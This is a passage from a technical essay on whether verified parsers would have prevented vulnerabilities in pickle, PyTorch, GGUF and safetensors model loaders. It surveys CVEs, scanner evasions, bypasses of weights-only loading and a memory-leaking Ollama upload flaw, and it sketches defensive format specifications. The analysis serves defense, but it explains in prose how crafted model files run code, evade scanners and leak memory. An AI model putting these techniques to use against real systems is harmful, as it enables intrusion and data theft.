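This older version of pickle has no opcode for raw bytes, so Python stores the text 'abc' with a call to a function that converts it to bytes. The GLOBAL opcode reads the names of a module and a function from the file, imports the module if necessary and pushes the function onto the stack. The REDUCE opcode pops the function and its arguments, calls the function and pushes the result.

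Ordinary pickle doesn't restrict these names. An attacker can replace `encode` with a function that runs operating-system commands without changing the sequence of opcodes. Other opcodes besides REDUCE are also dangerous. *SafePickle* (Ohayon, Gilkarov and Dubin, 2026) counts 68 opcodes, six of which can lead to code execution. GLOBAL is one of them because it can import a module, which runs the module's top-level code.

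Python's *pickle* module once checked whether a function was marked as safe before the REDUCE opcode called it. The developers removed these checks in Python 2.3 and wrote in the source comments that they had abandoned "any pretense" that pickles from strangers might be safe to load. According to the module's manual page, users should load only data they trust.

### A correct parser for a dangerous language

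The theorems about verified parsers need a specification p that maps bytes to a value, and for pickle it isn't obvious what the value should be. It could be the list of opcodes. A parser that returned this list would be fairly easy to verify, because most opcodes consist of one byte and an argument of fixed or declared length. But the parser would also return the correct list for the attacker's file, and the pickle machine would then execute the attacker's call.

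The value could also be the finished object. The specification would then have to define what REDUCE does for every function that a Python program can import, including those that delete files or open network connections. For the attacker's file, the specified behavior would include running the attacker's command, so a parser that didn't run it could not be proved correct.

A verified parser would still accept a malicious pickle file that is well formed. The comments in Python's source code list a "pickle verifier" among ideas for future tools, but it would only check that a pickle is well formed. A verified parser would prevent memory errors in the code that reads opcodes, but attackers hardly need such errors when a pickle can call functions. Any protection therefore has to start by limiting what the format allows a pickle to do.

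### Weights-only loading

Python lets a program override the function that looks up the names in GLOBAL instructions. PyTorch goes further and has a separate pickle reader for its weights-only mode. This reader calls only the functions and builds only the classes on an allowlist, and it never imports a module while loading. The allowlist covers what a state dict (a dictionary that maps the names of a model's parameters to tensors) needs. Comments in PyTorch's source code mention, for example, `torch.nn.Parameter` and Python's `OrderedDict`. Users can add entries to the allowlist.

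The mode has been PyTorch's default since version 2.6. Before the change, the developer mikaylagawarecki told users in *BC-Breaking Change* that plain state dicts would load as before. Files containing a whole pickled model would fail unless users switched the mode off, and files with NumPy arrays would need extra allowlist entries.

In *PickleBall*, Kellas, Li and colleagues (2025) measured how often the default list is too short. They took the 1,500 most popular Hugging Face repositories that offered models only as pickles, and could analyze 1,426. In 219 of those (15.4%), at least one model used a function or class that the list does not allow. Users had downloaded these repositories 79.6 million times in a month.

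When a file fails to load, PyTorch shows an error message with two options, extending the list or turning the mode off, and a warning to turn it off only for trusted files. Some libraries make this choice for their users. The text-analysis library flair turns the mode off because its models need functions outside the list.

### Flaws in the restricted reader

OSV's *CVE-2025-32434* (2025) records a flaw in PyTorch 2.5.1 and earlier, rated 9.3 out of 10 for severity, that let a checkpoint run an attacker's code even in weights-only mode. Ji'an Zhou, who found it, points out in OSV's *GHSA-53q9-r3pm-6pq6* (2025) that PyTorch's documentation had presented the mode as safe. According to a comment in Red Hat's *CVE-2025-32434 python-torch* (2025), PyTorch could load an older, tar-based checkpoint format only in the unsafe way, so it ignored the weights-only setting for those files. Version 2.6.0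 added a check that prevents this.

PyTorch never used the weights-only reader for tar files, so a proof about that reader would not have helped. A useful proof would have to cover the whole loading function, including the code that detects a file's format.

Zhou also found the next flaw, which OSV's *GHSA-63cw-57p8-fm3p* (2026) describes and rates 8.8. It was in the weights-only reader itself and had two causes. The SETITEM opcode adds a key and a value to a dictionary, which must lie below them on the stack, according to Python's comments. PyTorch's reader did not check that the object there was a dictionary, so a file could apply the opcode to another kind of object and corrupt memory. The reader also did not check the number of elements a file declared for a block of data against the data actually in the archive.

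A verified reader would have prevented both errors, a missing type check on the stack and a missing length check of the kind EverParse generates for network packets. PyTorch fixed them in version 2.10.0. On the Red Hat (2026) bug tracker, a contributor called such flaws real security issues for users because weights-only loading is "supposed to be a safe function".

OSV's *PYSEC-2026-139* (March 2026) reports that version 2.10.0 also had a flaw, unsafe deserialization in the code that loads pt2 files, another PyTorch format. An exploit was public, although the attacker needed local access, and the project had not yet responded. The record does not identify the faulty function, so it is unclear whether a verified parser would have helped.

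*ShadowPickle* (Pradhan, Nambiar and Soremekun, 2026) gets past the weights-only mode by changing what an approved name refers to. The pickle references `OrderedDict`, which is on the allowlist, but the attacker has overwritten the module that contains it. The paper describes this as the first attack to bypass the mode, but the tar flaw had already allowed a bypass the year before. The attack depends on tampering with the victim's Python environment, so it is a weaker objection to the reader than Zhou's findings. But it shows that any proof would have to assume that approved names still refer to the original code.

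### Policies for each library

A single allowlist is too narrow for some libraries and too broad for others. PickleBall, a tool by Kellas and colleagues, derives a separate policy for each library from that library's source code.

The analysis starts with the class of model that the library's loading function returns. If the class has a method that specifies which function pickle should call on loading, PickleBall adds that function to the policy and examines the types of its arguments. Otherwise, it adds the class itself and examines its subclasses and the types of its attributes. It repeats this for every new type until none are left. The policy has two lists, one of names that a pickle may import and a much shorter one of functions that it may call.

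A modified version of Python's pickle module then enforces the policy. If a file imports a name that is not on the list, the module creates an empty placeholder and raises an error only when something tries to use it. This is useful because many models contain leftovers from training, such as optimizer settings, that aren't needed to run the model.

Kellas and colleagues tested PickleBall on 252 harmless models from 16 libraries and 84 malicious ones, and compared it with PyTorch's mode and two scanners, ModelScan and ModelTracer:

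| Tool | Malicious models stopped or detected (of 84) | Harmless models accepted (of 252) |
|---|---|---|
| PickleBall | 84 | 201 |
| Weights-only mode | 84 | 157 |
| ModelScan | 75 | 236 |
| ModelTracer | 44 | 252 |

PickleBall took a median of 14 seconds to generate a policy and slowed unpickling by a median of 1.75%. The share of models it could load varied a lot between libraries. It loaded all 76 models made with sentence_transformers, but only 15 of 51 for YOLOv11, an image-recognition library whose models refer to its classes by inconsistent names.

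PickleBall's perfect score against malicious models doesn't show that it would stop an attacker who had studied a policy. Nearly all of these models came from earlier searches of Hugging Face and were not written to defeat PickleBall. They called functions that no model has any reason to call. Such an attacker could instead try to combine functions that the policy permits, and the policies leave some room for this. For YOLOv11, the policy allowed 1,816 imports and 61 calls, while the models used 63 and 11. Kellas and colleagues knew of no such attack but left open whether one was possible.

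The PickleBall paper states a guarantee that, given correct information about the types in a library, the tool blocks every call that the library's models do not need. No proof assistant has checked this guarantee, and its condition is hard to meet in Python, where a program can add attributes to an object at any time. The researchers also had to edit the source code of five of the 16 libraries by hand before the analysis worked.

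### What a proof about a restricted reader would have to state

An allowlist limits which functions a file can call, but not what those functions do with the arguments in the file. PyTorch warns that its weights-only mode does not prevent denial of service and that memory corruption may still be possible. A file can also load successfully but produce an object that causes an out-of-bounds access later. For example, a program might build a sparse tensor from two loaded tensors, one containing values and the other their positions, and some of those positions might be out of range.

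Proving that the reader calls only approved functions would therefore not be enough. Each approved function would also need a proof that it is safe for every argument a file can supply. Much of the code behind these functions is PyTorch's C++, which would take far more work to verify than a parser.

It would be easier to remove the calls altogether. The reader could treat an approved name as a label. When it came to the name of the function that rebuilds a tensor, it would record that a tensor with a certain shape belongs in this place, and call nothing that the file had named. Pickle would then be an awkward notation for data, and the usual methods would apply. The main theorem could read:

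For every byte string b, load(b) either fails or returns a structure of dictionaries, lists, text, numbers and tensors in which every tensor lies inside its storage. In both cases, naming a function in b does not cause load to run it.

A storage is a block of numbers that one or more tensors use. PyTorch's documentation has an example with a tensor of the numbers 1 to 9 and a second tensor that contains only the even ones. The checkpoint stores the nine numbers once. The second tensor has an offset of 1, a size of 4 and a stride of 2, so it uses positions 1, 3, 5 and 7 of the storage, counting from 0. For a tensor with sizes d1 to dk, none of them zero, and non-negative strides s1 to sk, the last position is:

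offset + (d1 − 1) × s1 + … + (dk − 1) × sk

The last position a tensor uses must be smaller than the number of elements in its storage. For a tensor with offset 1, size 4 and stride 2, that position is 1 + 3 × 2 = 7, which fits in a storage of nine elements. If the file gave the size as 5, the last position would be 9, just past the end because positions start at 0. The proof would also have to show that the sum cannot overflow. The reader must also check that the archive entry is as large as the pickle declares, which is 72 bytes for nine eight-byte integers. PyTorch lacked this kind of comparison until version 2.10.0.

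Some of the other theorems are harder to carry over. The memo lets a pickle put the same object in two places or build a list that contains itself, which a specification based on nested values cannot represent. State dicts don't need lists that contain themselves, so the reader could reject them. Non-malleability also fails, because Python can delete unused memo entries from a pickle without changing the result, and the six versions of the format encode the same integer in different ways. Termination is simple to prove once the function calls are gone, because the machine has no loops.

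This reader would accept roughly the same plain state dicts that the weights-only mode accepts now. Any program that can read them can also save them as safetensors, the format Hugging Face introduced as a safer replacement. A verified pickle reader might therefore be most useful as a converter that people run once on each old checkpoint.

### Scanners that misread files

Hugging Face allows pickles but scans them. Its scanner compares their contents with lists of allowed and forbidden items, and *The Art of Hide and Seek* (2025) describes such lists as inherently incomplete. A scanner that does not execute the pickle also has to read it exactly as the loader will, because an attacker can exploit any parser differential between them.

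Python executes each pickle opcode as soon as it reads it, so a malicious call near the start of a file that is corrupted further on has already run when the loader reports an error. A scanner that expects a well-formed file may fail without giving a verdict. The security company ReversingLabs found models of this kind on Hugging Face in 2025 and named the technique nullifAI. Ohayon and colleagues ran several scanners on four files from this incident and one other malicious file. PickleScan and ModelScan each detected four of the five, Fickling detected one, and the antivirus services ClamAV and VirusTotal detected none.

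A loader that followed the LangSec rule, for example by using a verified validator, would check the whole pickle before running the first opcode and reject the corrupted file. The attacker could repair the file, but then the scanner could read it too.

A file can also contain more than one pickle. Python's loader stops at the first STOP opcode and ignores any bytes after it. In the test by Kellas and colleagues, ModelScan also stopped there and missed a malicious part later in the file. Python would not normally have run that part, but another pickle could have loaded it in an unusual way. Pradhan and colleagues describe a related attack that uses several pickles in a row, which worked until scanners began to check past the first one.

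Attackers can also evade scanners by repackaging a malicious pickle. Ohayon and colleagues recreated nine evasive files from *The Art of Hide and Seek*, which hide a malicious pickle inside, for example, a ZIP, tar or bzip2 file. The existing scanners succeeded almost only on plain pickles. An attacker could also exploit ambiguities in ZIP archives so that the scanner reads a harmless pickle and PyTorch loads a different one.

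Scanners and loaders could avoid all these disagreements by sharing one verified parser, but the scanners would still miss many attacks. Of the nine malicious models that ModelScan failed to detect in the PickleBall test, five called functions that were not on its list of forbidden functions. Three fetched more code while running, and only the one with several STOPs exploited the way ModelScan parsed the file. Pradhan and colleagues note that more than a hundred packages in Python's public package index offer ways to execute code, so a list of forbidden functions can hardly be complete. Their overwritten-module attack had an evasion rate of 63% across ten scanners.

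### Detection by opcode statistics

SafePickle, the scanner that Ohayon and colleagues propose, calculates the percentage of each kind of opcode in a file and passes these percentages to a classifier trained on labeled files, without using a list of functions. They collected 648 harmless and 79 malicious files from Hugging Face. On the files reserved for testing, their best classifier detected 87.5% of the malicious files and cleared 96.9% of the harmless ones. The 87.5% is consistent with 14 out of 16 files, in which case one file would change it by about six points.

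The same type of classifier had mixed results on unfamiliar data. It detected all nine repackaged files and all five real malicious ones. On PickleBall's collection, it detected 93% of the malicious models but cleared only 60.8% of the harmless ones. PickleScan, an older scanner that relies on lists, detected 97.2% of the malicious models and cleared 92.6% of the harmless ones.

SafePickle also ignores function names. It cannot distinguish the harmless dictionary pickle from a copy that replaces `encode` with a dangerous function, because the opcodes are the same. Attackers who know this can imitate the statistics of an ordinary model.

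Published detection rates for the same scanner can differ widely. ModelScan cleared 236 of 252 harmless models in a test by Kellas and colleagues, but none in a test by Ohayon and colleagues on nearly the same collection. In the second test, a model counted as detected if ModelScan reported any issue, which may explain the difference. Ohayon and colleagues also estimate that about 98% of the files flagged as unsafe on Hugging Face are harmless, partly because scanners flag functions such as `getattr` that ordinary models often use. Users who see this many false alarms will probably start to ignore the warnings.

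### How much pickle remains

In March 2025, Kellas and colleagues examined 16,661 Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month, and 44.9% of them contained a pickled model. Repositories that offered only pickles had more than 400 million downloads a month. Including repositories that also offer safetensors raises the total to 2.1 billion, but this overstates the danger because many of those users will have loaded the safetensors version.

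Pickle is still widely used. Ohayon and colleagues report that users uploaded more than 1.3 million pickle-based files to Hugging Face over two recent quarters, compared with about 900,000 safetensors files. Some of these pickles hold no weights, such as the common training_args.bin, which stores the settings of a training run. Kellas and colleagues found pickled training settings next to fine-tuned versions of Llama 4, Qwen 3 and DeepSeek-R1, although the original developers had released the models as safetensors. Someone who chooses a safetensors model can therefore still download a pickle, and loading it in PyTorch depends on the same weights-only reader that needed repairs in 2026.

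### Keras files

Other model formats can also carry code. Kellas and colleagues name HDF5, which Keras has long used for saved models, as another format that permits executable content. Keras's JSON-based files can contain layers with embedded bytecode. A verified JSON parser would accept these layers too, and return the bytecode as correctly parsed text.

Restricting Keras files should be easier than restricting pickle, because most layers consist only of a type and some settings. A format specification could list the permitted layer types and the legal settings for each, and leave out the type that contains bytecode. Models with custom layers would then fail to load, much as whole pickled models fail in PyTorch's weights-only mode. Keras would also have to apply the restriction to every file format it accepts, or an attacker could use an older one, as with PyTorch's tar files.

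## Which flaws in GGUF and safetensors loaders would a verified parser have prevented?

GGUF and safetensors files hold counts, names, lengths and raw numbers. Loading them never requires calling a function specified in the file, so the main objection to verifying pickle doesn't apply to them. Auditors have still reported more than 30 problems in the two formats' loaders and the code around them.

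### The two layouts

The first 24 bytes of a GGUF file contain the letters GGUF, a four-byte version number, and eight-byte counts of the tensors and the metadata entries. The metadata comes next, according to Debian's *gguf.md*, a copy of the format's documentation. Each entry has a key, a four-byte type code and a value. A string consists of an eight-byte length followed by that many bytes. An array begins with its element type and element count, and the elements can be arrays themselves.

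After the metadata, the file describes each tensor: its name, its number of dimensions (currently at most four), the size of each dimension, a code for the type of number, and an offset. The offset counts from the start of the data section, which begins at the next multiple of the file's alignment. The alignment is 32 bytes unless a metadata entry called general.alignment sets another value. A file with one metadata entry and one small tensor could look like this:

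| Bytes | Content |
|---|---|
| 0–3 | the letters GGUF |
| 4–7 | version 3 |
| 8–15 | number of tensors: 1 |
| 16–23 | number of metadata entries: 1 |
| 24–68 | general.architecture = "llama" |
| 69–109 | tensor "w", 2 × 3, four-byte numbers, offset 0 |
| 110–127 | padding |
| 128–151 | the six numbers |

A safetensors file starts with an eight-byte length, followed by a JSON header of that length and then the data. The header for the same tensor could be:

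```
{"w":{"dtype":"F32","shape":[2,3],"data_offsets":[0,24]}}
```

This text has 57 characters, so the data occupies bytes 65 to 88. The two offsets give the tensor's start and end within the data section. According to PyTorch's *Safetensors* project page, the library refuses headers larger than 100 MB.

In both formats, a loader can calculate a tensor's size from its shape and number type. It can also get a size from the offsets in a safetensors file or the bytes actually present in a GGUF file. Several of the worst flaws arose because a loader used one of these sizes without properly comparing it with the other.

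### Repeated overflows in one GGUF function

In January 2024, Databricks reported six flaws in ggml, the library that reads GGUF files for llama.cpp. Archibald explains in *GGML GGUF File Format Vulnerabilities* that five of them were heap overflows caused by unchecked arithmetic. In one, the loader stored a string by reserving one byte more than the length given in the file. If that length was 2^64 − 1, the sum wrapped around to 0. Lean's runtime had almost the same bug. In the other four overflows in ggml, the loader multiplied a count from the file by the size of one item, and the product could wrap around too. In the sixth flaw, the loader used a type code as a position in a table without checking it against the table's length.

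Talos' *llama.cpp GGUF library info->ne heap-based buffer overflow vulnerability* (2024) describes a seventh flaw, which Databricks had also found. The loader had room for four dimensions per tensor but copied as many as the file specified. The developers released fixes for all seven within a week of the first report.

Similar bugs were reported again in 2025 and 2026. In July 2025, NVD, the US government's vulnerability database, listed CVE-2025-53630, an integer overflow in the function that loads GGUF files, with a severity of 8.9 out of 10. NVD's *CVE-2026-27940* (2026) reports that the developers' fix "overlooked some areas" of the same source file. The loader could still reserve too little memory and then write at least 528 bytes of the attacker's data past the end of it. The title in Vulners' *CVE-2026-27940* places the overflow in the calculation of the total memory size.

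Another overflow affected the function that calculates the size of a single tensor. In an example from Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-33298* (2026), the function returned 4 MB for a tensor that needs exabytes. The loader's memory check then passed, and the program wrote past the buffer when it processed the tensor. OSV's *CVE-2026-52131* (2026) describes a less serious flaw, in builds up to b5693, that let an attacker trigger an assertion, a check that stops the program when a condition is false.

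The incomplete fix is a good argument for machine-checked proofs. A programmer who fixes an overflow also has to find every other calculation that uses numbers from the file. F* checks each operation and would have rejected the code until all of them were safe.

The proof would have to cover the code that reserves memory, though. If llama.cpp called an EverParse validator and then ran its existing allocation code, the unproved multiplications in that code would be harmless only if the format specification kept the numbers small enough.

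### A tensor of 2^64 bytes

A header could declare a tensor of 2^32 by 2^30 four-byte numbers. The tensor would have 2^62 elements and need 2^64 bytes, which a 64-bit counter stores as 0.

The safetensors library once had this flaw. *Safetensors Library Security Assessment* (Dahlgren, Hussain and colleagues, 2023) describes an audit that the security company Trail of Bits carried out for the research group EleutherAI. The library multiplied a tensor's dimensions by the size of one number and compared the result with the difference between the two offsets. If both offsets were 0, the tensor above would have passed, because its computed size was also 0. The program would then have had a tensor with 4.6 quintillion elements and no data.

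The library is written in Rust, which by default doesn't check for integer overflow in release builds. Rust does check array accesses, so the program would have stopped with a panic when it tried to read an element. In C++, the same kind of mistake led to the memory corruption in CVE-2026-33298.

In 3D, an author might start with the obvious constraint, in which `d0` and `d1` are the dimensions:

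```
d0 * d1 * 4 == end - begin
```

F* would reject it, since nothing guarantees that the product fits into 64 bits. The author would have to put two comparisons in front of it:

```
d0 <= DataSize / 4
&& (d0 == 0 || d1 <= (DataSize / 4) / d0)
&& d0 * d1 * 4 == end - begin
```

If the data section has 20 billion bytes, it can hold at most 5 billion four-byte numbers. The first dimension, 4,294,967,296, is below this limit. Dividing 5 billion by it gives 1, rounded down, and the second dimension is far greater than 1. The parser therefore rejects the tensor before it multiplies anything. For any shape that passes both comparisons, the product is at most the size of the data section, so the multiplication cannot overflow. (The subtraction on the last line needs a similar check that `begin` does not exceed `end`.)

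Solvers such as Z3 are less reliable when a formula multiplies two unknown numbers, so a practical tool would probably put this test into a library function with its own proof, as 3D does with `is_range_okay`. If the specification uses unlimited whole numbers instead, the correctness theorem leads to the same check. The specification computes 2^64 and fails because the result isn't 0, so the code must fail too.

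The specification has to define whether a tensor with a zero-sized dimension is valid, or two correct-looking loaders could disagree. For example, a tensor of 2^40 by 2^40 by 0 has no elements, but a loader that multiplies the dimensions from left to right overflows before it reaches the 0. A loader that multiplies from right to left gets 0 without overflowing.

### The rest of the safetensors audit

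Two consultants spent a week on the audit in March 2023 and reported ten findings, none of high severity. The library contained no unsafe Rust code, so the flaws led mainly to crashes and parser differentials. This supports Poll's advice to switch languages first, although a week is too short to find everything.

The library checked that the tensors followed one another without gaps, but not that the last one ended at the end of the file. If the file was too short, the program panicked when it accessed a missing tensor. If the file was too long, the library ignored the extra bytes. Dahlgren and colleagues used this to build polyglots (files valid in two formats) that combined safetensors with Keras, PDF, ZIP or TFRecords. One program could load such a file as a harmless safetensors model while another loaded a malicious Keras model from it.

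JSON caused a different kind of inconsistency. If a header contains the same tensor name twice, the official library rejects it, Python's built-in JSON parser keeps the last entry, and a popular Go parser keeps the first. Some independent safetensors loaders already used the more permissive parsers, so a single file could produce different weights in different programs. JSON parsers have also differed in how they handle large numbers and escaped characters.

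Hugging Face had resolved nine of the ten findings by the time the auditors returned in April 2023. The library now rejects bytes after the last tensor and checks the size calculation for overflow. It also validates the ranges that callers request when they read part of a tensor. For duplicate names, the developers improved the documentation, but someone can still write an independent loader that doesn't follow it. They also added a warning and a confirmation step to a script that could run an attacker's code when it converted pickled models to safetensors.

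They also tried to forbid zero-sized tensors but had to reverse the change because PyTorch and other libraries produce them. Microsoft's engineers faced the same risk of rejecting input from existing software, in their case older guests in Hyper-V. Anyone who writes a format specification for model files would have to test it on a large collection of real models first.

Polyglots are still possible after these fixes. A tensor may contain any bytes, including a complete ZIP archive, and ZIP readers start at the end of the file. If the last tensor holds such an archive, the archive's bytes all belong to a tensor, so the file is valid safetensors and a verified parser would correctly accept it. The dependable remedy is for programs to decide in advance which format they expect, because safetensors has no signature at the start of the file. The auditors recommended adding a signature and a version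 number.

They also recommended replacing the JSON header with a binary one, so that developers could describe the whole format in a language such as Kaitai Struct and generate parsers from it. EverParse also generates parsers from a format description, but it verifies them. The format's header is still JSON.

### The Ollama leak

Ollama has its own GGUF loader, written in Go. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-7482*, Ollama servers before version 0.17.1 accepted uploaded files in which a tensor's declared offset and size went past the end of the file. When the server later quantized such a model, converting its weights to a more compact type of number, it read past the end of a buffer and stored the adjacent memory as weights.

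That memory might contain access keys, system prompts and other users' conversations, according to Debian's *CVE-2026-7482*. The attacker could then have Ollama upload the finished model to a server they chose. None of these steps required a password. Ollama by default accepts connections only from its own machine, but Cyera's *Bleeding Llama* (2026) counts about 300,000 servers reachable from the internet.

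Go is a memory-safe language that checks array accesses, so the faulty read must have gone through code outside that protection, such as a call into C. A verified parser might not have prevented the read either, because every field in the uploaded file could be valid by itself and the bad read happened later, during quantization. The parser would have rejected the file only if its specification required each tensor to end within the file.

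*Bleeding Llama* (Suiche, 2026) presents a detector, written by an AI agent, for such files. According to the agent, ggml's loader tracks how many bytes remain in the file and does not read past them, unlike Ollama's. The detector compares each tensor's declared size with the bytes available and also looks for overlapping tensors, offsets that do not increase, incomplete blocks of quantized weights and dimensions of zero. Apart from the rule about zero, these checks would fit well into a format specification. If both loaders had used parsers generated from one such specification, they would have applied the same checks.

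### An automated audit of the GGUF readers

An advisory posted to Openwall's security mailing list in May 2026 lists six more weaknesses in llama.cpp's two GGUF readers. Hermes Agent, an AI agent from Nous Research, found them the day it was posted, so the advisory includes no reply from the developers.

The weakness with the highest rating, 9.1, is that the C++ reader accepts any power of two as the alignment, however large. With an alignment of 2^31, rounding up a position in a small file gives a position about 2 GB in, far past the end. On a 32-bit machine, the calculation can also overflow. The rating seems too high for 64-bit machines, where the rounding works as intended and a program that jumps past the end of a file finds nothing to read.

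The reader also doesn't follow the format's documentation, which requires a multiple of 8. It accepts 2 and 4 but rejects 24. The fix proposed in the advisory would still accept 4. Anyone writing a format specification would have had to resolve this mismatch.

The Python reader has no limit on the number of dimensions, although the C++ reader rejects more than four. A file that declares the largest possible number of dimensions makes the Python reader request about 32 GiB of memory. According to the advisory, the limits of one gigabyte for strings and about a billion elements for arrays are also so high that a file could exhaust the machine's memory.

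The other three weaknesses look less serious. The C++ reader mixes signed and unsigned numbers in its counts, and it reads type codes without immediately checking their range. It could also divide by zero, but only if ggml's table contained a block size of zero for a valid type, and a malicious file cannot change that table.

### The ten flaws presented at DEF CON 34

Cyera presented ten flaws in llama.cpp at DEF CON 34, a hacker conference in August 2026. The company audited GGUF metadata and two other areas, but none of the ten public records describes a flaw in the GGUF parser.

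Two of the flaws let the server use memory it has already freed. An optional feature removes the model from memory when the server is idle. *CVE-2026-43631* (2026), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute (INCIBE), explains that a request arriving at the wrong moment could use the model's vocabulary after the server had freed it. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-43632* (2026) describes the same problem in six other server functions. Both flaws have a severity score of 9.2.

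Two more flaws arise when llama.cpp restores saved state, such as the KV cache, which holds intermediate results for text the model has already processed. In INCIBE's *CVE-2026-43629* (2026), the program uses a count from the saved file in an unchecked multiplication and writes past its buffer. In OSV's *CVE-2026-43630*, an oversized number makes it read past the end of an array. The attacker needs write access to the directory with the saved files. These files have their own format, so a GGUF parser would not process them. A verified parser for that format could stop both attacks if the program passed it the size of the destination buffer, much as 3D's TCP description receives the segment's length.

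The code that runs the model contains another unchecked multiplication, in the function that prepares a batch of tokens (INCIBE, *CVE-2026-43627*, 2026). MITRE's *CVE-2026-43628* lists an integer underflow in a sampler, the code that chooses the next token.

The last four flaws are in an example program that connects llama.cpp to Android apps. VulnCheck, the company that assigned the identifiers, describes a multiplication that can overflow when given a value from a model file or the app. The program also releases memory with the wrong function and lets one thread free memory that another is using.

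A verified parser would not have prevented the remaining Android flaw, because the app would still crash after the parser rejected a corrupt file. According to VulnCheck, the program doesn't check whether a model has loaded before it runs a benchmark, so a corrupt or truncated file crashes the app. A stricter parser could make such crashes more common by rejecting more files.

Cyera began reporting its findings in July 2025. The developers closed several reports without a fix, and five of the ten flaws were still present on June 1, 2026. Verified parsing would have prevented few, if any, of them, so the slow response strengthens the case for better maintenance more than for verified parsers.

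### A specification for GGUF

A specification for GGUF in the style of 3D could look like this, where `FileSize` is the length of the whole file:

```
typedef struct _TENSOR_INFO(UINT64 FileSize, UINT64 Start) {
  GGUF_STRING name  { name.len <= 64 };
  UINT32 n_dims     { n_dims <= 4 };
  UINT64 dims[n_dims];
  UINT32 type       { is_known_type(type) };
  UINT64 offset     { offset == Start && offset <= FileSize
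                      && tensor_fits(dims, type, FileSize - offset) };
} TENSOR_INFO;

typedef struct _GGUF(UINT64 FileSize) {
  UINT32 magic         { magic == 0x46554747 };
  UINT32 version       { version == 3 };
  UINT64 tensor_count  { tensor_count <= FileSize / 24 };
  UINT64 kv_count      { kv_count <= FileSize / 13 };
  METADATA kv[kv_count];            // supplies Align
  TENSOR_INFO infos[tensor_count];  // supplies End
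  PADDING(Align) pad;               // ends at DataStart
  // final check: DataStart <= FileSize
  //              && FileSize - DataStart == End
} GGUF;
```

The file's size limits the two counts because every item takes up space. A tensor's description needs at least 24 bytes, even with an empty name and no dimensions, and a metadata entry needs at least 13. A file of 2,400 bytes therefore cannot describe more than 100 tensors. If a loader uses 240 bytes of memory for each description, its table can be at most ten times as large as the file. With these limits, the multiplications that caused the 2024 overflows cannot wrap around for any file of realistic size.

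`Start` is 0 for the first tensor. For each later tensor, it is the end of the previous one, rounded up to the alignment. Tensors therefore cannot overlap, and every offset is a multiple of the alignment. `Align` must be a power of two between 8 and 1,048,576, which satisfies both the documentation and the C++ reader. The upper limit is the one the advisory proposed.

The parser can check that a tensor lies inside the file only after it has read every tensor's description. Offsets are measured from the start of the data section, and the parser can't locate that section earlier. Until then, it compares each size with the length of the whole file, which is enough to keep the arithmetic from overflowing.

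The final check would have stopped the Ollama leak. It requires `End`, the position in the data section where the last tensor ends, to equal the length of that section. In the 152-byte example, the data section starts at byte 128, so it is 152 − 128 = 24 bytes long, and the tensor ends at position 24. Because the tensors follow one another in order, this check ensures that all of them lie inside the file and that no bytes follow the last one.

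Some of these rules are stricter than the documentation, which doesn't require tensors to appear in order. It specifies padding between tensors but not whether any follows the last one. Anyone writing a real specification would have to check what existing files do and perhaps allow final padding.

### What the sketch leaves out

3D could not process this specification as written. It measures arrays in bytes, but GGUF gives the number of metadata entries and tensor descriptions, which vary in length. A 3D type also cannot pass a running position such as `Start` from one array element to the next. A developer could use actions for both, as Microsoft did for one Hyper-V message, but then no theorem would show that the actions enforce the layout. This weakness is serious because the check against the Ollama leak depends on that running position.

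The alignment is also awkward because it may appear anywhere in the metadata, and the parser needs it later to find the data section. One solution is to read the metadata twice, first to find the alignment and then to parse the file with that value as a parameter. The specification should also forbid duplicate keys, because if a file had two alignment entries, two readers might look for the data in different places.

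Nested arrays require recursion, which 3D lacks. An author could allow a fixed number of levels and write a separate type for each, or forbid nesting if no important model uses it. Otherwise, the counter from EverCBOR would work with a small change. The validator would count only the arrays left to validate. It would skip an array of numbers in one step and check the strings in an array one at a time. For an array of arrays, it would add the number of inner arrays to the counter. Each array header takes 12 bytes, so the remaining length of the file limits the counter.

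The size of a tensor in bytes depends on its quantization type. Most types pack weights into blocks. Q4_0, for example, stores 32 weights in 18 bytes, with four bits per weight and a shared two-byte scale, so a tensor with 4,096 weights has 128 blocks and takes up 2,304 bytes. The number of weights in a row must be a multiple of 32. The documentation lists 32 current types by number but doesn't give their sizes, so whoever writes the parser's specification has to take them from ggml's source code. If the specification and the code used different sizes, the parser would approve tensors that the program then misread. Developers could avoid this by generating both tables of sizes from the same file. They would also have to regenerate the parser for each new type.

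The hard part of parsing safetensors is the JSON header. It nests only a few levels deep, so its parser does not need general recursion, but it does need rules for spaces, number formats, escaped characters and duplicate names. Because `"\u0077"` is another way to write `"w"`, the parser must decode names before comparing them. The simplest specification would accept only headers formatted the way the official library writes them, but files from other programs might then fail to load. If the header may list tensors in any order, the parser must also sort them by offset before checking for gaps and overlaps.

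Both formats let programs map a file into memory, so that the operating system loads parts of it only when the program uses them. Another program with write access can then change the file after the parser has checked it. A loader can protect the header in a similar way to Hyper-V's virtual switch, by copying it into private memory, parsing the copy and never reading the header from the file again. The weights can stay in the mapped file, since a changed weight gives wrong results but cannot move a tensor's boundaries. If somebody shortens the file, the program may still crash when it reaches the missing part. Such changes matter mostly on shared storage, because an attacker who can write to a private model file could replace the model before it loads.

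### Sorting the flaws

It is uncertain whether anybody has published a verified loader for GGUF or safetensors. The EverParse and Vest papers do not cover either format.

The table therefore describes what such a loader could do. "Yes" means any verified parser would have prevented the flaw, if its proof also covered the code that reserves memory and fills the loader's tables. "If specified" means a verified parser would have prevented the flaw only if the format specification stated the rule in the last column.

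| Flaw | Prevented? | Reason or required rule |
|---|---|---|
| GGUF, 2024: unchecked counts, lengths and type code | Yes | memory and arithmetic safety |
| GGUF, 2024: more than four dimensions | Yes | memory safety |
| CVE-2025-53630 and CVE-2026-27940: too little memory reserved | Yes | arithmetic safety |
| CVE-2026-52131: assertion stops the program | Yes | a verified parser returns an error |
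| Python GGUF reader: unlimited dimensions | Yes | the parser checks that enough bytes remain |
| GGUF advisory: number conversions, type codes, division by zero | Yes | arithmetic safety and range checks |
| CVE-2026-33298: tensor size wraps around | If specified | the tensor's size must fit in the file |
| CVE-2026-7482: Ollama leak | If specified | each tensor must end within the file |
| GGUF advisory: alignment | If specified | upper limit on the alignment |
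| GGUF advisory: memory exhaustion | If specified | limits on strings and arrays |
| Safetensors: size overflow | If specified | shape and offsets must give the same size |
| Safetensors: missing or extra data | If specified | the last tensor must end where the file ends |
| Safetensors: duplicate names | If specified | names must be unique, in every loader |
| Safetensors: archive hidden inside a tensor | No | the file is valid |
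| Safetensors: unchecked ranges from the caller | No | the ranges do not come from the file |
| Safetensors: conversion script runs pickle code | No | the danger lies in the other format |
| CVE-2026-43629 and CVE-2026-43630: saved state | No | separate format, which needs its own parser |
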